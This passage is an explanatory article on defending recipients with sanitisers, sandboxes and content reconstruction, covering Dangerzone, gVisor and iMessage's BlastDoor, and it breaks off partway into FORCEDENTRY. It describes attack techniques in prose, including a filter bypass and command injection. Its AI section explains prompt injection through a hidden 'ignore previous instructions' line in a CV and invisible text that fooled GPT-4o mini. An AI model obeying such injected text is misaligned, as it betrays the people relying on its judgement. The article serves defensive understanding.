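# Sanitising and sandboxing what untrusted software and AI systems send to people

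## What sanitisers, sandboxes and interpreters do

Sanitisers, sandboxes and interpreters can help protect a recipient who has no good reason to trust a message's sender. A *sanitiser* is a program that removes, replaces or rebuilds parts of data so that the result cannot trigger unwanted actions in the program that receives it. A *sandbox* is a restricted environment in which a program can reach only the files, networks and other programs that its operator has given it. An *interpreter* is a program that reads instructions and carries them out step by step, so it can block or limit any of them. Engineers use all three in web browsers, mail programs and phones, and now also on what AI systems write.

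### An invoice on its way to the reader

Suppose a clerk in an accounts department receives an emailed invoice containing a few lines of formatted text, the supplier's logo and a link to a payment page. Formatted email uses HTML, the markup language of web pages, so the message arrives as a description of a page. Several programs must process that description before the clerk sees anything. An attacker can target any of these programs or the clerk, and has six kinds of attack to choose from.

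The mail server's spam filter usually processes a message before anyone reads it. The filter works on the message's source, while the clerk reads what appears on the screen, and the two can differ. *Too salty to handle*, a 2025 analysis by Cisco's security researchers at Talos, collects examples. One fraudulent email imitating the American tool shop Harbor Freight looked entirely English, but its source contained French words, hidden by a style rule, that confused Microsoft's language detection. In another, the sender had put invisible characters between the letters of the brand name Norton LifeLock, which hinders any filter that searches for the name. Both emails are examples of the attack of *showing the reader something other than what is there*, as is a link that displays one address and leads to another.

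Next the mail program has to turn the source into a page. It does this with a *parser*, the part of a program that turns incoming bytes into a structure it can use, such as a picture or a list of fields. An *exploit* is input built to make a program do something its designers did not intend, and parsers are a natural target because they have to process whatever the sender sends. In May 2026 SecurityWeek reported a "use-after-free" flaw in a library that Microsoft's Word and Outlook share. The program went on using a piece of memory after releasing it, so an attacker who got data into that memory could take over what the program did next. Haifei Li, who found the flaw, warned that reading or previewing an email triggered it, even if the user clicked nothing. According to the security company Field Effect, this happens because Outlook uses the library to display the email.

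The logo needs its own parser. *The Seven Turrets of Babel*, by Momot, Bratus and colleagues, describes a bug in how Adobe Reader handled BMP pictures. A BMP file can contain commands that move a cursor to where the next pixels belong, and Reader did not check that the cursor stayed inside the picture. A crafted file could therefore write its "pixels" anywhere in memory. This bug and the one in Outlook are both cases of *corrupting a parser's memory*.

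HTML can also carry programs, and *smuggling in active content* means placing such a program where the recipient's software will run it. Mail programs restrict JavaScript, the usual language for this, so the attacker may have a better chance with the page the link opens, or with a web-based accounting system that later displays the invoice's text.

An attacker can gain by *making the display fetch or send data*, even if no code runs. If the logo sits on the sender's server, the mail program may request it when the clerk opens the message, and the sender then learns that somebody has opened it, and when. Cisco Talos found senders using style rules to track readers' actions and preferences. Security engineers call it *exfiltration* when private data leaves in this way.

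The office may also have an AI assistant that summarises the inbox. A line of white text on a white background could make it list this supplier as approved. This is a *prompt injection*, which is text placed in material an AI model reads so that the model treats it as an instruction. *Injecting instructions into an AI model* is the newest of the six attacks, and the term "prompt injection" dates from 2022.

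The invoice may also be false. Every program works as its designers intended, but the clerk pays money into a thief's bank account. *Persuading or deceiving the reader* requires no exploit, and it is lucrative. The FBI's Internet Crime Complaint Center (IC3) puts 2025 losses from business email compromise, which includes more than false invoices, at $3 billion, second only to losses from investment fraud.

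### Containing, cleaning and refusing

A system's *attack surface* is all the code that untrusted input can reach. *The Rule Of 2*, from Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's Chrome browser, allows any piece of that code to combine at most two of three risks: untrustworthy input, a programming language that does not prevent memory errors (commonly C or C++), and high privilege, meaning roughly the power to do whatever the user can do. The rule emphasises memory errors because, as of March 2019, all but about 5 of Chromium's 130 public critical-severity bugs were obviously memory corruption.

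A browser has to process untrusted input, and rewriting old C++ code takes years, so the remaining option is to remove privileges with a sandbox. The program that decodes the logo runs in its own process, which cannot open the user's files or connect to the network. If the logo contains an exploit, the attacker gains control of a process that can do very little.

The sandbox limits the damage if parsing goes wrong, but the process inside it can still return a result that a more privileged program has to read. A sanitiser limits what that result can contain. PNG, a common picture format, is complicated, and its C implementation has had memory bugs. Chromium's engineers therefore have the sandboxed process convert the PNG into a bare bitmap, which contains only pixel values, the image's size, and a few facts about how to read them. The privileged program accepts nothing else, and it reads the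 bitmap with a parser small enough to test thoroughly. An attacker who has taken control of the decoder can choose the pixels, and ideally nothing else. The code that carries the bitmap across the boundary is itself written in C++ for speed, and a bug there could still allow a *sandbox escape*, an exploit that lets code inside the sandbox act outside it. But the engineers have far less code to search for such a bug.

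Some messages contain instructions that the recipient wants to carry out, such as a spreadsheet formula or a short program that an AI assistant has written to add up the month's invoices. Removing them would defeat the purpose. An interpreter can run these instructions while limiting what they can do. For example, it might provide arithmetic and read access to one folder, but no command that opens a network connection.

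Such arrangements have a mixed record, often because the language they offered was too powerful. The search engine Elasticsearch let users write parts of their queries in Groovy, a general-purpose programming language, and its developers tried to filter out the dangerous parts. They left in reflection, which lets a program look up and call other parts of the system by name, and attackers could then run any code they liked on the server. Momot and colleagues think a small language made only for queries would almost certainly have prevented this. They write that sandboxing a general-purpose language leads to "an endless fount of sandbox escapes". Capping the amount of work does not help much either. Ethereum, a cryptocurrency, charges a fee for every operation in a contract, which limits how much a contract can do but not what the operations can do in combination. In 2016 a thief used recursive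 calls, which the rules allowed, to drain an investment fund called The DAO.

### Three ways to sanitise

The most obvious method is to delete anything that matches a list of known bad patterns, called a *denylist*. MITRE's *CWE-184*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, gives the example of a function that tries to stop JavaScript by removing the word "script" from its input. An attacker can bypass this filter by writing the word in capitals.

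In a worse example from the entry, a program builds an operating-system command out of a user's name, after replacing risky characters with their HTML codes. Its author forgot to include the semicolon, which on a command line ends one command and lets another begin. The attacker doesn't even have to type a semicolon. They can type an apostrophe followed by a command, and the sanitiser will replace the apostrophe with its HTML code, which ends in a semicolon.

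A denylist covers only attacks that somebody has already thought of, even after capital letters and semicolons are added to it. The attacker chooses the next attack, often after trying variants on a copy of the filter until one gets through. There are many variants to try because, as MITRE points out, a single character can be encoded in many ways, and some characters mean something in one program and nothing in another. MITRE advises using denylists to notice suspicious activity and relying on something else for protection.

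An *allowlist* admits only what it names and rejects everything else, including attacks that nobody has invented yet. For the invoice, it might admit paragraphs, bold type and tables, but not style rules, scripts or remote pictures. Honest senders' messages may come out plain or broken, and each complaint is a reason to lengthen the list. An allowlist also gives no protection if the program that displays the message does something unexpected with a permitted element, such as a table.

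The remaining method, known in the security trade as *content disarm and reconstruction*, extracts the wanted content from a file, discards the file, and builds a new one from the extract. Chromium's bitmap is a small instance, and Dangerzone, a converter for suspicious documents, treats whole pages the same way. This removes a hidden script without anyone having to find it, because the script is never copied. It also removes anything else the extract can't represent, so the link stops working once the invoice is turned into pixels. The Chromium engineers describe the approach as finding a simple enough format and "committing to its limitations".

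Rebuilding has two weak points. First, something still has to parse the original. Everfox, a vendor of such systems, acknowledges that a checker complex enough to inspect a PDF in detail may have exploitable flaws. That is a good reason to run the checker in a sandbox. Second, a well-formed value can still be hostile. Chromium gives the example of a file path that parses correctly but leads outside the folder it is supposed to stay in. Similarly, rebuilding a picture that shows a thief's account number leaves the number unchanged.

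### Recognising input before using it

Allowlists and rebuilding both work only if someone can state what good input looks like. That is the central demand of LangSec, short for language-theoretic security. LangSec researchers treat a program's valid inputs as a formal language, a set of strings that a grammar defines exactly, and the input-handling code as a *recogniser*, which must decide whether a given string belongs to the set. One LangSec slogan is "Full Recognition Before Processing!", meaning that no other part of the program may touch the input until the recogniser has accepted all of it.

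If the clerk's company let suppliers submit invoices as single lines of text, the grammar could be this short:

```
invoice  → supplier ";" amount ";" due
supplier → eight digits
amount   → one to seven digits, ".", two digits
due      → four digits, "-", two digits, "-", two digits
```

The line `20418837;1250.00;2026-11-30` fits the grammar. The program rejects a line that contains a script or has nine digits in the supplier field, and does not try to repair it by trimming the extra digit. Momot and colleagues oppose such repairs because attackers like to use them to assemble an attack from harmless-looking pieces. They blame the popularity of PDF and Flash among attackers on the readiness of both formats' parsers to fix faulty files. The impossible date 2026-99-99 also fits the grammar, so later code still has to check that the date exists, but it can rely on the field containing digits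 in the right places.

Most software checks input less strictly. Its checks are scattered through the program, and by the time one fails, other code has already acted on part of the input. LangSec's proponents call this shotgun parsing. The Heartbleed bug in OpenSSL, a library that encrypts much of the web's traffic, came from a failure to reject invalid input. Each request included the length of its contents. An attacker could give a length greater than the true one, and OpenSSL would process the request anyway and send back whatever lay next to it in memory. Momot and colleagues describe an exploit as a program written in crafted input, with fragments of the victim's code as its operations. Other researchers call the unintended computer that runs it a *weird machine*.

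LangSec measures the complexity of a grammar using the linguist Noam Chomsky's hierarchy, which sorts languages by the kind of machine needed to recognise them. *Regular* languages, such as the invoice lines above, need a machine with only a fixed number of internal states. Nested structures, such as brackets inside brackets, also need a stack to keep track of what is still open. If the machine with the stack has at most one possible move at each step, the language is *deterministic context-free*, which is LangSec's limit on complexity. The data format JSON can stay within this limit if its designers avoid dependencies between distant parts of a message.

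The line falls there because several parsers usually read the same message, as the spam filter and the clerk's screen do, and they need to interpret it the same way. An algorithm can decide whether two deterministic context-free grammars accept the same strings, but no algorithm can do this for context-free grammars in general. On Android phones, one component once verified the signature on an app package and another installed the package, but the two read the compressed file differently, so an attacker could install something other than what the phone had verified.

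To show that the approach would help, Momot and colleagues reviewed the 47 security flaws reported in OpenSSL between January 2015 and June 2016. They estimated that a design based on LangSec would have prevented 35 of them, or 74.5%; the other 12 mostly concerned cryptography or the timing of parallel operations. These estimates come from people who favour the method and rest on bug reports for one library, and nobody rebuilt OpenSSL to test them. But even if a third of the 35 were wrongly counted, about half the flaws in this cryptographic library would still have involved reading input.

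For complex formats, full recognition can be undecidable, which means no program can check every input correctly. Recognition also does little to prevent valid input from causing harm later. Erik Poll, a computer scientist at Radboud University, separates flaws in *processing* input from flaws in *forwarding* it. In a forwarding flaw, an application reads a string correctly but hands it to a database, an operating system or a browser, where the string acts as a command. Poll considers it a mistake to try to prevent this by escaping dangerous characters on arrival. The reason, as MITRE's semicolon example suggests, is that nobody yet knows which program will eventually read the text, and a code that is harmless in a web page can be an attack on a command line.

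### Filters that face the AI model

Filters may need to protect people from what an AI model writes, but they also have to protect the model from what people and web pages send it. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C describes a recruiter whose system uses a model to score CVs. One candidate hides a sentence in their CV that tells the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve them for interview.

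Hidden text can also fool a model that serves as a filter. Researchers at Cisco Talos gave GPT-4o mini, a small OpenAI model, the source of a phishing email about an expiring password. The model correctly classed it as a request for action. When the email also contained invisible text, the model classed it as an attempt to schedule a meeting. This was a demonstration with one small model, so it doesn't show how often the technique succeeds. One of the remedies Talos proposes is an ordinary sanitiser that strips invisible text before the detector reads the message.

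That removes hidden instructions and leaves the visible ones. Web developers faced a similar problem with SQL injection, where text typed into a form reaches a database and runs as a command. They solved it with parameterised queries, which pass the command and the typed text to the database separately, so the typed text never runs as a command. David C argues that language models offer no such separation. A model predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, and that text includes both its developer's instructions and a stranger's CV. He thinks prompt injection may never be completely preventable. Denylists work especially badly here, because there are endless ways to rephrase "ignore previous instructions".

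Others are more hopeful about grammars. *CBCL* (2026), a LangSec-based design for messages between AI agents, cites an argument by von Hippel and Miyazono that AI security is fundamentally a LangSec problem, and that the main points of attack include the parsing of a model's structured output and its use of tools. The argument is convincing for those points. When a model calls a payment tool, for example, the request has fields, and a recogniser can check every one. But a grammar will accept the English sentence "please use our new account from now on" whether a supplier or a thief wrote it.

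David C therefore advises limiting what a successful injection can achieve, using ordinary code that restricts the system's actions whatever the model has read. He cites a rule from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista that when a model processes information from some party, its privileges drop to that party's. Under that rule, the clerk's assistant may summarise the stranger's invoice but cannot pay it while reading it.

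## Dangerzone: turning a suspicious document into pixels

Dangerzone is a free desktop program that converts a suspicious document into a new PDF made of pictures of its pages. Micah Lee, a journalist and software developer, wrote it in 2020 for reporters at The Intercept, an American news site. Reporters can't follow the usual advice to avoid opening strangers' attachments, because opening them is part of the job. The Freedom of the Press Foundation, a US non-profit that builds security tools for journalists, took over Dangerzone's development in 2022, in partnership with Lee. The foundation's *Dangerzone receives favorable audit* calls the result a "virtual photocopy". *Digital safety*, a guide from Reporters Without Borders (RSF), compares the process to printing a document and scanning it back in, and warns that Dangerzone does not replace an antivirus program.

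### From file to pixels and back

Suppose the clerk's invoice had arrived as a Word file. Without opening it, the Dangerzone application starts a *container*, a group of processes that Linux keeps apart from the rest of the computer, and feeds the file in as a stream of bytes. On Windows and macOS, the container runs inside a Linux virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system. Inside the container, the office suite LibreOffice converts the invoice to PDF, and the PyMuPDF library then draws each page as a grid of pixels. For every page, the container returns a width, a height and three numbers per pixel, giving the amounts of red, green and blue.

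Outside the container, the application assembles these numbers into a new PDF, one page at a time. If the user wants searchable text, an optical character recognition (OCR) program reads the pictures and adds a text layer, so the clerk can still copy the invoice number.

The container has no network connection, so malware inside it cannot send the document to anyone. This also blocks *canary tokens*, which an engineer from the Freedom of the Press Foundation described in a conference talk as silent alarms in documents. Like the remote logo in the clerk's email, a token alerts its owner when somebody opens the file, which could be disastrous for a reporter with a leaked document.

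The container returns raw colour values instead of a finished PDF or PNG because raw values need hardly any parsing. Chromium's sandboxed decoder returns a bare bitmap for the same reason. The receiving program reads the image's width and height, then multiplies their product by three bytes per pixel to get the exact number of bytes it should receive. Any byte sequence of that length is a valid picture, so the program can meet LangSec's requirement of full recognition by checking the dimensions and counting the bytes.

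### Why the developers distrust their own container

The Foundation's engineers assume that a document will eventually take control of the container. LibreOffice and its supporting libraries read many complicated formats, and some of that code is always out of date. In December 2023, the security company Include Security scanned the container's 305 software packages and found 79 matches with publicly known vulnerabilities. The one critical match was in Ghostscript, a program that processes PDF files. Many such flaws can be exploited only under very specific conditions, but an attacker who designs the document can try to create those conditions.

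The Foundation's *Dangerzone 0.8.1 is out* (2024) gives a more direct example, warning of flaws in a media library that could let an Office document with embedded Vorbis or Opus audio run arbitrary code inside the container. Users could not avoid the danger by refusing a particular type of file, because these documents looked like any others. The developers wrote that they expect vulnerabilities of this kind and that they knew of no way for such code to escape the container.

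The attacker's next step is to escape the container, and an ordinary container makes this easier than it should be. All the containers on a machine share the Linux *kernel*, the core of the operating system, which controls memory, files and devices. To open a file or send data, a program must make a *system call* to the kernel. An attacker who controls LibreOffice can therefore make system calls too, and a bug in how the kernel handles one of them may give access to the whole machine. The kernel is very large and mostly written in C.

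A separate virtual machine for each document would offer better isolation than a container. Qubes OS, a security-focused operating system whose "trusted PDF" feature inspired Dangerzone, works this way. The Dangerzone team tried virtual machines too, but found them hard to maintain across several operating systems. The engineer who gave the talk defended containers as harm reduction, because users would otherwise open the file directly on their laptops.

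### Adding a second kernel

In *Safe Ride into the Dangerzone*, Métaireau, Pyrgiotis and Perot (September 2024) explained how the team had strengthened the container with gVisor, which puts a substitute kernel between the container and Linux. Google released gVisor as open source in 2018 and uses it, among other things, when scanning Gmail attachments for viruses. Operators of AI systems also use it to contain code that a model has written.

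When LibreOffice tries to open the invoice, gVisor's main component, the *Sentry*, intercepts the system call and handles it with its own code. The Sentry is written in Go, a language that prevents most memory errors, and it leaves out much of what Linux has to support, such as hardware devices. The Sentry has no permission to open files itself, so it passes the request to the *Gofer*, a separate process outside the document's container. The Gofer checks the request, opens the file and gives the Sentry access to it, so LibreOffice gets the same result as it would from Linux.

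The remaining component is a *system-call filter*, which limits the calls Linux accepts from the Sentry. It forbids opening files, creating network connections and starting other programs, so an attacker who has broken out of LibreOffice and into the Sentry still cannot do these things directly. To reach the rest of the machine, they need another flaw in Linux that the few permitted calls can trigger.

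gVisor works only on Linux, and most of Dangerzone's users have Windows or macOS. The developers solved this by putting gVisor itself in a container. The outer container carries gVisor to whatever machine the user has, and gVisor then starts an inner container for the document. Métaireau and colleagues compare version 0.7.0, the first with gVisor, with version 0.6.1:

| Protection | Version 0.6.1 | Version 0.7.0 |
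|---|---|---|
| Linux kernel | Document's container calls it directly | Document's container calls gVisor instead |
| System-call filter | Moderate | Strict |
| Container's file system | Writable | Read-only |
| User's account | Mapped into the container | Not mapped |
| Network | Disabled | Disabled in both containers |

The row on the user's account matters if malware escapes. In version 0.6.1, it would have had the user's rights and could have read their documents and browser data. The improvement since then depends on a feature available from version 4.1 of Podman, the program that manages the containers on Linux. gVisor slows down programs that make many system calls, but document conversion makes relatively few.

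A good test of the sandbox came in April 2026, when researchers published copy.fail, an exploit that gives any ordinary user full control of Linux systems dating back to 2017. The Freedom of the Press Foundation (2026) reported that it could in theory have affected every Dangerzone user. The developers ran the exploit inside the sandbox and it failed, because it attacks a cryptographic interface that gVisor does not implement. This was only one exploit, and the developers ran the test themselves, but gVisor had blocked access to the flaw before it was publicly known.

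### The audit and later flaws

The most thorough outside examination is Include Security's *Security Assessment of Dangerzone's Web and Client Applications* (2024), which reports on a 12-day audit in December 2023 for the Open Technology Fund. The auditors gave themselves a command line inside the containers, as if an exploit had succeeded, and tried to get out but failed. They reported ten findings, three of them low risk and seven "informational". One of the low-risk findings concerned LibreOffice, and the auditors recommended switching off its macros and other active content. The Foundation replied that Dangerzone already opened documents with macros disabled and that it would disable the other features.

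This result is reassuring, but it applies to an older version of Dangerzone. gVisor has since made the container harder to escape, but another change may have weakened the protection slightly. In 2023 Dangerzone built the new PDF in a second container. According to the Foundation's *Changelog*, since version 0.8.0 the application has built it directly on the user's computer, outside any container, while the first container is still drawing pages. The developers consider this no less safe, because only pixels leave the first container.

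That is convincing for the step that turns pixels into PDF pages, but less so for optical character recognition (OCR). Include Security had suggested that an attacker might craft a page that looks like a jumble of broken pixels and exploits the OCR engine. The auditors thought such an attack unlikely but potentially severe, and had no time to build a working example. With OCR in a second container, a successful attacker would still have needed to escape it, but OCR now runs outside the container. Users who are worried about this and don't need searchable text can leave OCR switched off.

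Pixels have not always been the only thing to leave the container. Tenable's *CVE-2023-39342*, an entry in a vulnerability database, concerns the command-line version of Dangerzone, which printed the container's log messages in the user's terminal. Terminals obey certain control codes in the text they display, so a compromised container could have used them to fake messages or change the window's title. The developers fixed this in version 0.4.2 by cleaning the text before printing it. The problem seemed minor until April 2026, when a security team disclosed a flaw in iTerm2, a popular macOS terminal, that allowed untrusted output to trigger actions. The Dangerzone developers tried a file containing that exploit's control codes, and their program replaced the codes with harmless symbols.

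A converter can also fail by leaving something out. A bug introduced in version 0.4.1 could drop the last page of a document, which is serious if that page contains the signature or the exceptions. The developers fixed it in version 0.5.0 and began testing the program on about 11,000 documents.

Much of the developers' recent work concerns updates. The container used to come with the installer, so replacing one vulnerable library meant testing a full release on every operating system. Version 0.10.0, from December 2025, introduced separate updates for the container. If the user has enabled them, the application checks for them at most once every 12 hours. In the Foundation's *Dangerzone 0.10.0 released* (2025), the developers also report moving from LibreOffice 7 to LibreOffice 25.

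An update channel gives attackers a new way in, and a forged container could omit gVisor. The developers therefore sign each container and record the signature in a public log, and the application will not roll back to an older container. Anyone can build the container from the published source code and check that the result matches the distributed one bit for bit.

Version 0.11.0 followed on 2 July 2026, and the developers have since released 0.11.1. The Foundation's *Dangerzone 0.11.0 released* (2026) reports that OCR now works on several pages at once, up to six times faster in internal tests, and that Windows users can install the program from the Microsoft Store. The Foundation also plans to use Dangerzone in SecureDrop, its system for receiving files from anonymous sources. Its *Security audit of new SecureDrop Inbox completed* proposes sanitising documents before they reach the printer,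 which also has to parse them.

### What a page of pixels can hide

An attacker who controls the container can choose every pixel, and so can hide a message in the image. Hiding data in something that looks innocent is called *steganography*. The simplest method for pictures stores one bit in the last binary digit of each colour value. Changing a pixel's red value from 200 to 201 changes that digit from 0 to 1, and nobody looking at the page will notice.

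The amount of room depends on the resolution. The Foundation's *Replace pdftoppm logic with PyMuPDF (native python)*, the code change that introduced the PyMuPDF renderer, sets it at 150 dots per inch. A sheet of A4 measures about 8.27 by 11.69 inches, which gives 1,240 by 1,754 pixels:

```
1,240 × 1,754                 = 2,174,960 pixels
2,174,960 × 3 colour values   = 6,524,880 bytes   (about 6.5 MB)
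6,524,880 × 1 hidden bit      = 6,524,880 bits
6,524,880 / 8                 =   815,610 bytes   (about 800 KB)
```

The pixels of a single page, even a blank one, can hold the plain text of a novel. Data that a sender hides in the invoice's logo will probably be lost, because PyMuPDF redraws the logo at a new size and blends neighbouring pixels. Malware inside the container can avoid this loss by writing the final pixel values itself.

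The hidden data could be a complete virus and still not harm the clerk, because a PDF viewer only paints the value 201 as a shade of red. For the virus to run, another program would have to collect the last digits, join them and execute the result. An attacker who has already installed such a program on the clerk's computer doesn't need the invoice to break in, though the invoice might be a discreet way to send the program new commands.

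Someone who receives the converted document may also be able to decode data hidden in its pixels. Suppose a reporter converts a leaked document to remove the *metadata*, such as the name of the person who last edited it, and then publishes the result. Malware in the container could have copied that name into the pixels, where anyone who knew the scheme could read it. The malware would first need a working exploit against LibreOffice or another program in the container. A company looking for a leaker could more easily give each employee a copy with slightly different spacing between the words. Dangerzone will reproduce the spacing because it is part of the picture.

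JPEG compression destroys most of the last digits because it rounds away fine detail, but lossless compression preserves every hidden bit. Dangerzone compresses its PDFs, though this may not remove any hidden data. Overwriting the last digit of every value with a random one would reliably wipe out the 800 kilobytes calculated above. An attacker could respond by hiding fewer bits and repeating each one across a larger patch of the page, which may survive both JPEG and the random digits. In practice, a sanitiser can greatly reduce the amount of data a page can hide, but can't reduce it to zero while the page remains readable.

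### Files that people can still edit

Commercial content disarm and reconstruction usually aims to produce a usable file, such as a new Word document with the original's text, tables and pictures but not its macros. This is far more useful in an office than a stack of page images. But Word still parses the new file with its usual code, so an attack that depends on how Word handles a permitted element may survive. Dangerzone lets only pixels through, which leaves an attacker much less to exploit.

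It's also harder to judge how well a commercial product works. Include Security could read Dangerzone's source code, and so can anyone who doubts its findings. Many commercial products are closed source, and a vendor's count of the attacks it has blocked leaves out the ones it missed.

In both approaches, the program that takes the original apart may itself be vulnerable, as Everfox acknowledged. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) advises organisations in this position to *transform* incoming data into a simple format and then *verify* it in a separate place. The transforming program does the dangerous parsing on the untrusted side, and the verifying program on the protected side only has to handle the simple format.

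An organisation can connect the two with a link that carries data in one direction only. The strictest version is a *data diode*, for example an optical fibre with a transmitter at one end and only a receiver at the other. An attacker who gets a file across cannot use the same link to receive stolen data, or to see the file's effects and send commands in response. The restriction also affects honest senders, because the receiving side cannot confirm that a file arrived or ask for a damaged one again.

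Dangerzone follows much the same plan on a single laptop. The container transforms the document, and the application checks the stream of pixels it outputs. But the link between them is software, and both sides share a processor. The engineer who gave the talk pointed out that hardware flaws such as Spectre and Meltdown, which let one program read another's data through the processor, have no good remedy here.

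Pixels also leave a verifier little to check. If a supplier sends `20418837;1250.00;2026-11-30`, a verifier can reject an amount over some limit or a supplier number that isn't on file. With a picture of the same invoice, it can check only the dimensions. An organisation that needs only three fields from each invoice would do better to extract those.

The NCSC's *Cross domain approach and architecture* (May 2026) covers data flows between systems with different levels of trust. It warns against treating protection for these flows as "a single appliance" that eliminates risk. The guidance comes mainly from defence and intelligence work, and it assumes attackers who can obtain exploits for unknown flaws and chain several together. Some of Dangerzone's users face such attackers, but most accounts departments don't, so a converter on the clerk's computer is probably a reasonable choice for them.

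### What the user loses and what gets through

Dangerzone turns a spreadsheet into pictures of its cells, so a reporter can see a ministry's figure but not the formula behind it. Links no longer work, and nobody can edit the text. Blind readers lose the headings, table structure and picture descriptions that screen readers rely on, and OCR at best restores the words. The Eclectic Light Company's *How to open a suspicious document or app* describes a brief trial on a Mac in which the pages looked good, but OCR struggled with grey text and the program had trouble with very long single-page PDFs. The application took up 2.2 GB, and it does not handle audio or video.

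Some PDFs carry a cryptographic signature that lets the recipient check who issued them. Conversion removes the signature but keeps the letterhead, which can help a forger. A genuine invoice and a good imitation are both just pictures afterwards, so a clerk who needs to tell them apart should keep the original or, better, telephone the supplier on a number already on file.

Conversion leaves false statements unchanged. A web address on the page is no longer a link, but the clerk can type it into a browser, and some PDF viewers make addresses in a text layer clickable again. A phone can still scan a QR code on the converted page.

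Conversion gives some protection to an AI model that later reads the file, because the model no longer receives certain kinds of text that were hidden from the clerk. White text on a white background becomes pixels the same colour as the page around it, so it disappears. Invisible characters disappear too, because they draw nothing, and type one point high is only about two pixels tall at this resolution, too small to read. But an instruction in ordinary black type for the office's assistant to approve the supplier will still be on the page, and OCR will copy it into the text layer for the assistant to read.

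## BlastDoor: how iMessage isolates incoming messages, and two attacks on it

A phone starts parsing a message as soon as it arrives, whereas a reporter can leave a suspicious document unopened until Dangerzone has converted it. A notification might show the sender's name, the first few words and a small picture, and the phone has to decode all of these before its owner knows there is a message. On iPhones, a service called BlastDoor does most of this parsing for iMessage, Apple's messaging system. Apple introduced BlastDoor with iOS 14 in 2020. It parses each message inside a sandbox and passes a simpler version to the rest of the phone.

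### Attacks that need no click

In 2016, attackers tried to install spyware on an activist's iPhone by sending text messages with links, but the attack could work only if the activist tapped one. A *zero-click* attack doesn't require a tap, because the exploit is in the message itself and runs while the phone parses it. According to Ian Beer and Samuel Groß of Project Zero, a Google team that looks for unknown security flaws, an attacker who uses iMessage has to know only the target's phone number or Apple account name.

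The best-known seller of such attacks is NSO Group, an Israeli company that sells spyware called Pegasus to governments. Citizen Lab, a University of Toronto group that examines the phones of activists and journalists for spyware, lists some of NSO's earlier zero-click exploits in *FORCEDENTRY* (Marczak, Scott-Railton and colleagues, 2021). In 2019 NSO used a flaw in WhatsApp's calling feature against more than 1,400 phones in two weeks, and in 2020 it used an iMessage exploit known as KISMET. Exploits like these cost millions of dollars to develop, so few people become targets. The clerk with the invoice is unlikely to be one of them, but the clerk's phone handles every incoming message the same way an activist's does.

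Groß describes BlastDoor in *A Look at iMessage in iOS 14* (2021), based on about a week of reverse engineering. He explains that a zero-click attack using memory corruption usually needs a bug that a message can trigger, a way to locate things in the phone's memory, a way to use the bug to take control of a program, and probably a sandbox escape. Locating things is difficult because iOS loads its system libraries at random addresses, a defence called *address space layout randomisation* (ASLR). Groß found that iOS 14 made each of these steps harder.

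### A message's path through the phone

Suppose the clerk's supplier sends an iMessage with a link to a payment page. In iOS 14, at least seven separate programs handle it:

| Program | What it does with the message |
|---|---|
| apsd | Receives it from Apple's servers |
| identityservicesd | Decrypts it |
| imagent | Directs the work and hands the raw bytes to BlastDoor |
| BlastDoor | Parses the bytes and returns the contents as separate fields |
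| IMTransferAgent | Downloads any attachment |
| IMTranscoderAgent | Passes the link's preview data to BlastDoor |
| IMDPersistenceAgent | Stores the message and triggers the notification |

Splitting the work among several programs lets Apple give each one only the rights it needs. For example, only apsd and IMTransferAgent need network access. Before iOS 14, imagent did the main parsing itself.

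BlastDoor decompresses the message, decodes its structure, and checks that each field has the expected type. Any formatted text arrives as HTML, which BlastDoor also decodes. It then returns a record, which looks roughly like this for a message that reads "Hello World":

```
plainTextBody   "Hello World"
content         "Hello World", running in the natural writing direction
participants    sender's address, receiver's address
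replyToGUID     identifier of the message this one answers
```

BlastDoor does not pass on the HTML. This is another case of content disarm and reconstruction, but the output is richer than Dangerzone's pixels because the phone has to identify the message text and the person to reply to. The fields have fixed types, so imagent can accept text or an identifier without parsing the sender's format.

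The link takes more work. The supplier's phone has already rendered the payment page, packed its title, description and preview picture into an archive, encrypted the archive and uploaded it to Apple's iCloud servers. The clerk's phone downloads the archive to make a useful notification. The archive format can describe complicated objects and has caused security bugs, so BlastDoor unpacks the archive too.

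### Swift, a strict sandbox and slow restarts

Apple wrote most of BlastDoor in Swift, a language it designed to be *memory-safe*. If a crafted message makes a Swift program try to write outside its reserved memory, the program normally stops, so an attacker may be able to crash the parser but can't take control of it.

The rewrite was incomplete. Groß found that Swift code controlled the parsing, but BlastDoor still passed XML to an existing C library and archives to an existing unpacker in Objective-C, an older Apple language that doesn't prevent memory errors. A hostile message could still reach this older code, so the code needed a sandbox.

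According to a comment in the sandbox's rules, the aim is to make BlastDoor "as close to compute-only as possible". It cannot open outbound network connections, use hardware drivers or touch most files, and it can contact only a handful of other services, mostly ones that keep logs or pass on notifications. The rules also list the system calls that BlastDoor should need. When Groß looked in January 2021, the phone logged calls outside this list but still allowed them, whereas Dangerzone's current filter blocks unlisted calls.

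Apple also blocked a way of defeating ASLR. An attacker could send a message whose exploit made the phone read from a chosen memory address. The phone automatically returned a delivery receipt if the system libraries were at that address, but imagent crashed without sending one if nothing was there. An attacker who chose the addresses well could find the libraries with about 20 messages. Since iOS 14, the phone has moved the libraries to a new random address after a crash of this kind, so what the attacker learned from earlier messages is no longer useful.

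The phone also waits longer and longer before restarting a service that keeps crashing. Groß tested this with a small program that crashed on purpose. The first restarts came ten seconds apart, then the interval doubled after each crash, up to 20 minutes. Twenty restarts therefore take about four hours, compared with just over three minutes if the interval stayed at ten seconds. A patient attacker still gets some attempts, but Groß also saw the phone report BlastDoor's crashes to Apple's servers, so repeated failures may attract attention.

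He judged the changes close to the best Apple could have done while remaining compatible with older software. Marczak and colleagues suspected that BlastDoor had stopped KISMET from working, and that NSO developed its next exploit in response.

### FORCEDENTRY: a GIF routine in the wrong place

In March 2021, Citizen Lab examined a Saudi activist's phone and found that it had been infected with Pegasus. Marczak and colleagues later re-examined a backup of the phone and found 31 suspicious files with names ending in ".gif" that had arrived just before the infection. Twenty-seven were actually copies of the same tiny Photoshop file, and each copy had crashed IMTranscoderAgent. The other four were PDFs. The researchers named the exploit FORCEDENTRY and believe NSO had been using it since at least February 2021.

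The attack got past BlastDoor because of a minor feature. Apple wanted animated GIFs in iMessage to repeat forever, even if the sender's file said to play them once. To change that setting, the phone first made a copy of the file, using a routine with "copyGif" in its name. Beer and Groß found that the routine decoded the whole picture and drew it again into a new file, rather than just copying the bytes. It did this in IMTranscoderAgent, outside BlastDoor, before the owner saw anything.

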